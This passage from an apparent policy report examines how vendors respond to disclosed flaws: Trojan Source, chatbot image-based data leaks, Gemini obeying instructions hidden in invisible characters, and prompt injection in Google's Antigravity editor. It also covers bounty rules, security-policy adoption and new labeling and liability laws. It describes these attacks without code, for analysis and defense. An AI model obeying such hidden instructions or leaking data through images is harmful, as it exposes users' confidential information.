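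| User | Attention and interruptions | The user and her employer | The user, for clicking or approving |

Anderson and Moore cite a long-standing principle of legal theory that liability should fall on the party that can best manage the risk. For leaks through images and links, that party is the assistant vendor, which controls the chat window and the policy sent with it. Superhuman could tighten its policy within days, but Maria could not have changed hers.

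Business customers are often responsible for software they cannot control. SearchLeak used parts of Microsoft's service that administrators cannot change. But under EU data protection law, a company whose assistant leaks personal data normally has to notify the authorities within 72 hours, even if the fault was in a supplier's software.

The same split can occur inside a single company. Microsoft built the Teams preview service and Bing's image search for purposes unrelated to Copilot, and the people who ran these services had little reason to expect that an AI assistant would send stolen data to them. Removing a convenient feature would have been a loss for those teams and a benefit to Copilot's customers. A large company can in principle weigh the two, but only if someone is responsible for doing so.

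### How companies responded to Trojan Source

Companies rarely explain why they left a defense out, but disclosure records can show what they did once they knew about a problem. The best such record concerns Trojan Source, the attack that disguises source code with direction controls. Because the attack affected so many products at once, *Talking Trojan* (2022), Boucher and Anderson's study of the disclosure, treats it as a natural experiment and compares responses to the same report.

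In *Trojan Source*, Boucher and Anderson say they sent their first reports to 13 organizations in July and August 2021 and set a public release date 99 days after the first one. They eventually contacted 19 organizations, all of which confirmed receipt, and nine committed to releasing a fix. Eleven had programs that pay rewards for reported flaws, and five of those paid.

The responses varied even among products with the same weakness. The table draws on Boucher and Anderson and on the longer account by Boucher (2024), in *Deception and defense from machine learning to supply chains*:

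| Product | Response | Explanation or circumstances |
|---|---|---|
| Rust | Added a check to the compiler | Published the fix on the day of public release |
| LLVM, which underlies a common C compiler | Added checks to a separate code-checking tool | Wanted to avoid slowing down the compiler |
| Java | Closed the report as "Not a Bug" | Oracle said that the Java team doesn't make tools for reviewing code |
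| Node.js | Declined | A check would run only when the program does, so a false alarm could disrupt working software |
| Go and C# | Made no commitment | |
| Julia | Banned unclosed direction controls in comments and strings | Learned of the attack from the public release |

Oracle had a point, since the deception happens on the reviewer's screen. But either the language or the editor can block the attack, so language and editor developers can each blame the other. Boucher points out that this gives both groups an excuse to do nothing. The people most exposed are those who later run the code, and they may have no contact with either group.

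The approaching publication date did more than the report itself to get fixes out. Boucher describes this countdown as the part of a disclosure that pushes companies to fix their software. Official identification numbers for the flaws also drew noticeably more attention, although anyone could get one by sending a properly formatted email. Publication also reaches projects nobody thought to warn, as Julia's response shows.

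Rewards had a weaker effect. The five payments ranged from $525 to $5,000 and totaled $11,232. Two of the five organizations had initially refused to pay. Several companies used outside firms to screen reports. These firms often replied within hours but closed many reports as harmless because the attack didn't match a familiar type of flaw. Asking for a full-time employee of the company to review the report usually solved this.

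Reward programs can discourage researchers from warning everyone. The CERT Coordination Center, a US institute that helps spread confidential warnings, let the researchers reach many companies through one shared system, but companies typically don't pay for flaws reported that way. A researcher who wants the money does better approaching paying companies one by one, which leaves the others less time to prepare a fix. *Talking Trojan* (2022), a summary on the Cambridge security group's blog, Light Blue Touchpaper, calls this conflict potentially dangerous.

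The researchers had earlier found that similar characters could fool machine translation and filters for abusive language. They notified the companies responsible and suggested defenses, including ordinary code that cleans the text before it reaches the model. More than two years later, Boucher found virtually no changes except in Google Translate, which had become resistant to lookalike letters and invisible characters but not to direction controls.

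Boucher suggests several reasons for the delay: retraining a model is expensive, machine-learning teams are less used to shipping urgent fixes, and each side may expect the other to deal with the problem. But cleaning text doesn't require retraining, so that expense can't fully explain the delay. The comparison is also imperfect, because the researchers didn't submit these flaws to reward programs and the press covered them much less.

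### One image leak, three responses

In 2023, Johann Rehberger reported the same flaw to three AI companies, whose chatbots all displayed images from any address. The companies responded as follows:

| Product | Reported | Result | Time taken |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude | July 12 | Closed on July 26 | 14 days |
| Bing Chat | April 8 | Fixed by June 15 | 68 days |
| ChatGPT | Early 2023 | Declined at first, then added a partial check in December | Most of a year |

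Microsoft appears to have fixed Bing Chat mainly with a content security policy that allowed images from four of its own hosts, according to Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*. All four belonged to Bing, which SearchLeak used three years later to get data out of a different Microsoft assistant. Anthropic made users click before an image loaded. Rehberger considered this imperfect but agreed that it stopped the automatic leak.

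Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed* notes that OpenAI had marked the report as something it would not fix. Rehberger doesn't give a reason, but it was probably not the difficulty of the fix, since a competitor solved the same problem in two weeks by adding a button. In describing Microsoft's fix, Rehberger wrote that he hoped it would encourage OpenAI to follow. Such public comparisons put pressure on a company to act, because customers can see that a safer product is possible.

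### Google's refusal to filter hidden characters

FireTail, a security company that sells AI monitoring, told Google on September 18, 2025 that the Gemini assistant followed instructions written in invisible characters, according to BeyondMachines' *Cybersecurity experts warn of ASCII smuggling prompt injection vulnerability*. Google declined to act, and BGR's *Google Has No Plans To Fix This Terrifying Gemini Security Vulnerability* quotes its view that the attack "can only result in social engineering", which means tricking a person into doing something harmful. Android Authority's *Google says it won't fix Gemini security flaw* (2025) notes that this leaves the user responsible.

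Google, which makes both Gemini and Gmail, is much better placed than Maria to filter out tag characters. People can defend themselves against social engineering only if they have some chance of noticing it, and Maria's screen doesn't show text written in tag characters. Filtering them out would break little more than a few flag emoji. Google could reasonably argue that the filter would not catch visible instructions, but Maria can at least see a strange sentence in an email and question it.

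In the same tests, ChatGPT, Copilot and Claude resisted the hidden instructions, while Grok and DeepSeek did not. A later FireTail test suggests that Google's position had not led to broader protection by January 2026. *Peek a boo 🫣 emoji smuggling and modern LLMs* (2026) reports that a related trick worked on Gemini, and on Grok at the second attempt, but not on ChatGPT, Claude, DeepSeek or Meta's assistant. The two tests hid text in different ways, so DeepSeek's better result in the second doesn't prove that its developer had fixed the earlier problem.

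### Bug rewards for Antigravity

Google does pay for some flaws of this general kind. *Google Launches AI Bug Bounty Program with Rewards Up to $30,000* (Welle) describes a program whose examples include an attack that summarizes someone's email and sends the summary to a stranger. But Google doesn't pay for issues it already knows about. This condition appeared in its AI reward criteria (Google, 2023) and remains in its *Abuse Vulnerability Reward Program Rules*.

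The condition makes sense for a single bug, since Google learns nothing new from a second report, but a known issue can also be a whole class of attacks. When Google released its code editor Antigravity in November 2025, its list of known issues included prompt injection attacks that steal data or run an attacker's code. Willison (2025) notes that this made them ineligible for rewards, and that Google said it was working on fixes. In the meantime, a researcher who found a new way to steal data from Antigravity's users through prompt injection could expect no payment.

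Google had based Antigravity on code it licensed for about $2.4 billion from the maker of Windsurf, another editor. Rehberger had reported flaws in Windsurf that May and found them still present in Antigravity, according to Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE*. He writes that Google began listing them publicly only after researchers started sending reports, and guesses that its security team was caught off guard. Google relied on warning users about the risk, according to PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data*. A warning takes almost no effort to write, and it shifts some of the blame to users who continue after reading it.

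Google handled a later report differently. On January 6, 2026, Pillar Security told Google about an injection that let an attacker run code even in Antigravity's Secure Mode. Google patched the flaw on February 28 and paid a reward, according to CyberScoop. Secure Mode was supposed to enforce a boundary, so a way around it was a defect. In the earlier cases, Google had told users that the product might leak data. When a vendor promises a specific limit, researchers can test it, and a failure is harder to dismiss as expected behavior. OpenAI had also made no such promise when it declined the University of Washington's report on its browser.

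### How many websites use a content security policy

Browser makers can build a defense and still depend on millions of website operators to turn it on. The *Security* chapter of HTTP Archive's 2025 Web Almanac found a content security policy on 21.9 percent of websites, up from 18.5 percent a year earlier. Most of these policies are too weak to stop the attacks that stronger ones could address.

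Among policies that restrict scripts, 92 percent include a keyword that generally permits scripts written directly into the page, and 77 percent let scripts run text as code. Both weaken the protection against cross-site scripting. The first figure overstates the problem a little, because browsers ignore the keyword when the policy also contains certain stricter settings.

For an AI assistant, it matters more whether the policy restricts images. None of the six most common policies does, and they make up about 66 percent of policies on mobile pages and 59 percent on desktop pages. They do things like switching insecure connections to encrypted ones or preventing other sites from displaying the page in a frame. If the same proportions hold across all sites with a policy, fewer than one website in ten could have a policy that would stop a leak like Maria's.

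Most websites don't display a model's answers, so they have less need for such a limit. The figures are better evidence of how operators behave when a defense takes work. Report URI's *Ten years of web security* (2026) examined 170,057 policies from the million most popular sites in June 2026 and found the keyword for direct scripts in 46.8 percent. That is lower than HTTP Archive's figure, partly because Report URI counted all policies, not just those that restrict scripts. Report URI, which sells tools for monitoring these policies, also found that protections improved steadily where a hosting company could switch them on for its customers, but not where the site's own staff had to finish the configuration.

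Site operators have a reason to stop at a loose policy, because they can add one in minutes and truthfully tell customers that they have a policy. A strict policy may break advertising, analytics or an old part of the site, and the staff who maintain the policy will hear about the broken pages but not about the attacks it stopped.

Google had a stronger incentive to finish the work on its own sites, because it paid for each reported flaw and could see the benefit in its own accounts. According to Report URI's *Client-Side Security Reporting* (2026), cross-site scripting accounted for 30 percent of those payments in 2018 and 4.1 percent in 2023, after Google had adopted strict policies. Other improvements may have contributed to the decline.

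### Why platforms may not want AI labels

A content security policy protects a website even if no other site adopts one, but provenance labels depend on both camera makers and social networks. A camera maker gains little from signing photographs if social networks delete the signatures, and networks gain little from reading signatures that few cameras add. Anderson and Moore describe how such technologies can fail to spread because everyone waits for someone else to go first. Fax machines overcame this problem because companies first bought them to connect their own offices, where they were useful even if no one else had one. A news agency could use signed photographs internally in the same way, but a social network has no equivalent use.

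Platforms also have commercial reasons to hesitate before labeling AI content. They earn money from attention, and in Altay and Gilardi's experiments people were less willing to share headlines labeled as AI-generated, even accurate ones. Companies such as Google and Meta both run platforms and sell AI generators, so a label that makes viewers suspicious also reflects badly on their own tools. Uploaders may also object. In 2024, Meta changed its "Made with AI" label to "AI info" after photographers complained that it appeared on real photographs with minor edits.

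The harm from a missing label falls on other people. A viewer believes a false picture, or someone in Leeds leaves home because of a flood that never happened, while the platform keeps the advertising revenue. This doesn't prove that platforms leave out labels on purpose, since the audits of 2025 and 2026 also found generators that failed to mark their files. But the low labeling rates are what one would expect when the company that pays for a label gets little of the benefit.

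### What the law requires

Governments have begun to change these incentives, mostly for labels. The position in early December 2026 is as follows:

| Law | Who must act | Main duty | Date |
|---|---|---|---|
| China's labeling measures | AI services and platforms | Add visible labels and metadata. Platforms must also check uploads for them | In force since September 1, 2025 |
| EU AI Act, Article 50 | AI companies, and those who publish deepfakes | Mark AI output so that software can detect it, and tell people about deepfakes | August 2, 2026, with an extension to December 2 for marking by systems already on the market |
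| California AI Transparency Act | AI companies with over a million monthly users | Put hidden labels in images, video and audio, and offer a free detector | August 2, 2026 |
| The same act, as amended | Large platforms | Show provenance data to users and don't knowingly remove it | January 1, 2027 |
| EU Cyber Resilience Act | Makers of software and connected devices | Report flaws that attackers are using. Later, meet broader security requirements | September 11, 2026 for reporting, December 11, 2027 for the rest |
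| EU Product Liability Directive | Manufacturers, including software makers | Compensate people harmed by a defective product, without proof of negligence | Products placed on the market after December 9, 2026 |

California's amended act will also require makers of new cameras and phones to offer provenance labels from 2028.

China places duties on both the services that generate AI content and the platforms that distribute it. If a platform finds a hidden label in an upload, it must tell viewers that the content is AI-generated. If it finds no label but detects other signs of AI generation, it must mark the content as suspected AI. Article 50 of the EU AI Act mainly binds the companies that provide or use AI systems, so a social network that only hosts other people's pictures isn't its main target. For a large company, fines for violating Article 50 can reach €15 million or 3 percent of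 worldwide turnover, whichever is higher.

California's duty for platforms could make a large practical difference. In The Washington Post's 2025 test, all eight platforms removed the credentials from an AI video. From January, a large platform that knowingly removes labels in a widely adopted format will break California law where keeping them is technically feasible.

The Cyber Resilience Act addresses security more directly. It covers editors, browsers and other software sold in the EU, along with the online services a product needs to work. It generally doesn't cover services used only through a website. Since September, manufacturers have had to send an early warning within 24 hours of learning that attackers are exploiting a flaw in one of their products. This would not have applied to EchoLeak or SearchLeak, because nobody is known to have used either against real customers. Requirements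 more relevant to prevention start in December 2027, when manufacturers will have to ship products with secure default settings and handle reports of flaws through a published process. The default-settings rule could put pressure on manufacturers that make their strongest protection optional, as Lockdown Mode is in ChatGPT.

The Product Liability Directive counts software, including AI systems, as a product, and a missing security update can make a product defective. But it compensates only individuals, and only for certain kinds of harm. If an agent followed a hidden instruction and deleted Maria's family photographs, she might have a claim for the lost data. But if the agent leaked the plan to close the Leeds office, her employer would have no claim under the directive, because it is a company and its loss is commercial. The most common goal of these attacks is to copy confidential data,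 and the directive largely leaves the resulting losses with the victims. A business has to rely on its contract with the vendor, which the vendor usually writes.

None of these laws specifically requires a chat window to block outside images or a mail program to remove invisible characters. A court or regulator might treat such measures as part of reasonable security, especially now that several vendors have them.

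### Which pressures have led to deployment

Public disclosure has the clearest record of getting companies to deploy security defenses. Editors and code hosts added warnings around the time Trojan Source became public. Microsoft, GitHub, Salesforce and Superhuman changed their assistants after researchers reported a leak and prepared to publish it. Anderson and Moore cite earlier research on ordinary software, which also found that vendors release fixes faster when flaws become public, although attacks also increase.

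This evidence is somewhat biased toward disclosure, because researchers publish what they find, while companies rarely announce a defense they added at a customer's request. Disclosure also tends to produce narrow fixes. Microsoft patched one route through Bing after SearchLeak and had to close a second one five months later.

Business buyers have probably had some influence on vendors. OpenAI offered Lockdown Mode to organizations months before personal users could get it, which suggests it had corporate customers in mind. Large customers can also demand audits and permitted-host lists that an individual user could not get. But their influence depends on knowing what to ask for, and the vendor knows far more about its own servers than they do.

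Bug rewards seem to have mattered less than either. They encourage people to look for flaws and give them a proper way to report what they find, but companies have often made fixes without paying. Anthropic changed its fetching tool after Ayush Paul's report but gave him no reward. The sums in the Trojan Source case were too small to have influenced a large vendor's budget, and Google doesn't pay for known issues, which removes the incentive where a product is weakest.

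Liability has yet to show an effect because the new EU rules on defective software don't apply until next week. Specific legal duties in the EU have worked faster. They led AI companies to introduce text watermarks, and several companies released detectors around the August 2 deadline. But most detectors tested that month missed some of their own company's images, so someone still has to check whether the tools work.
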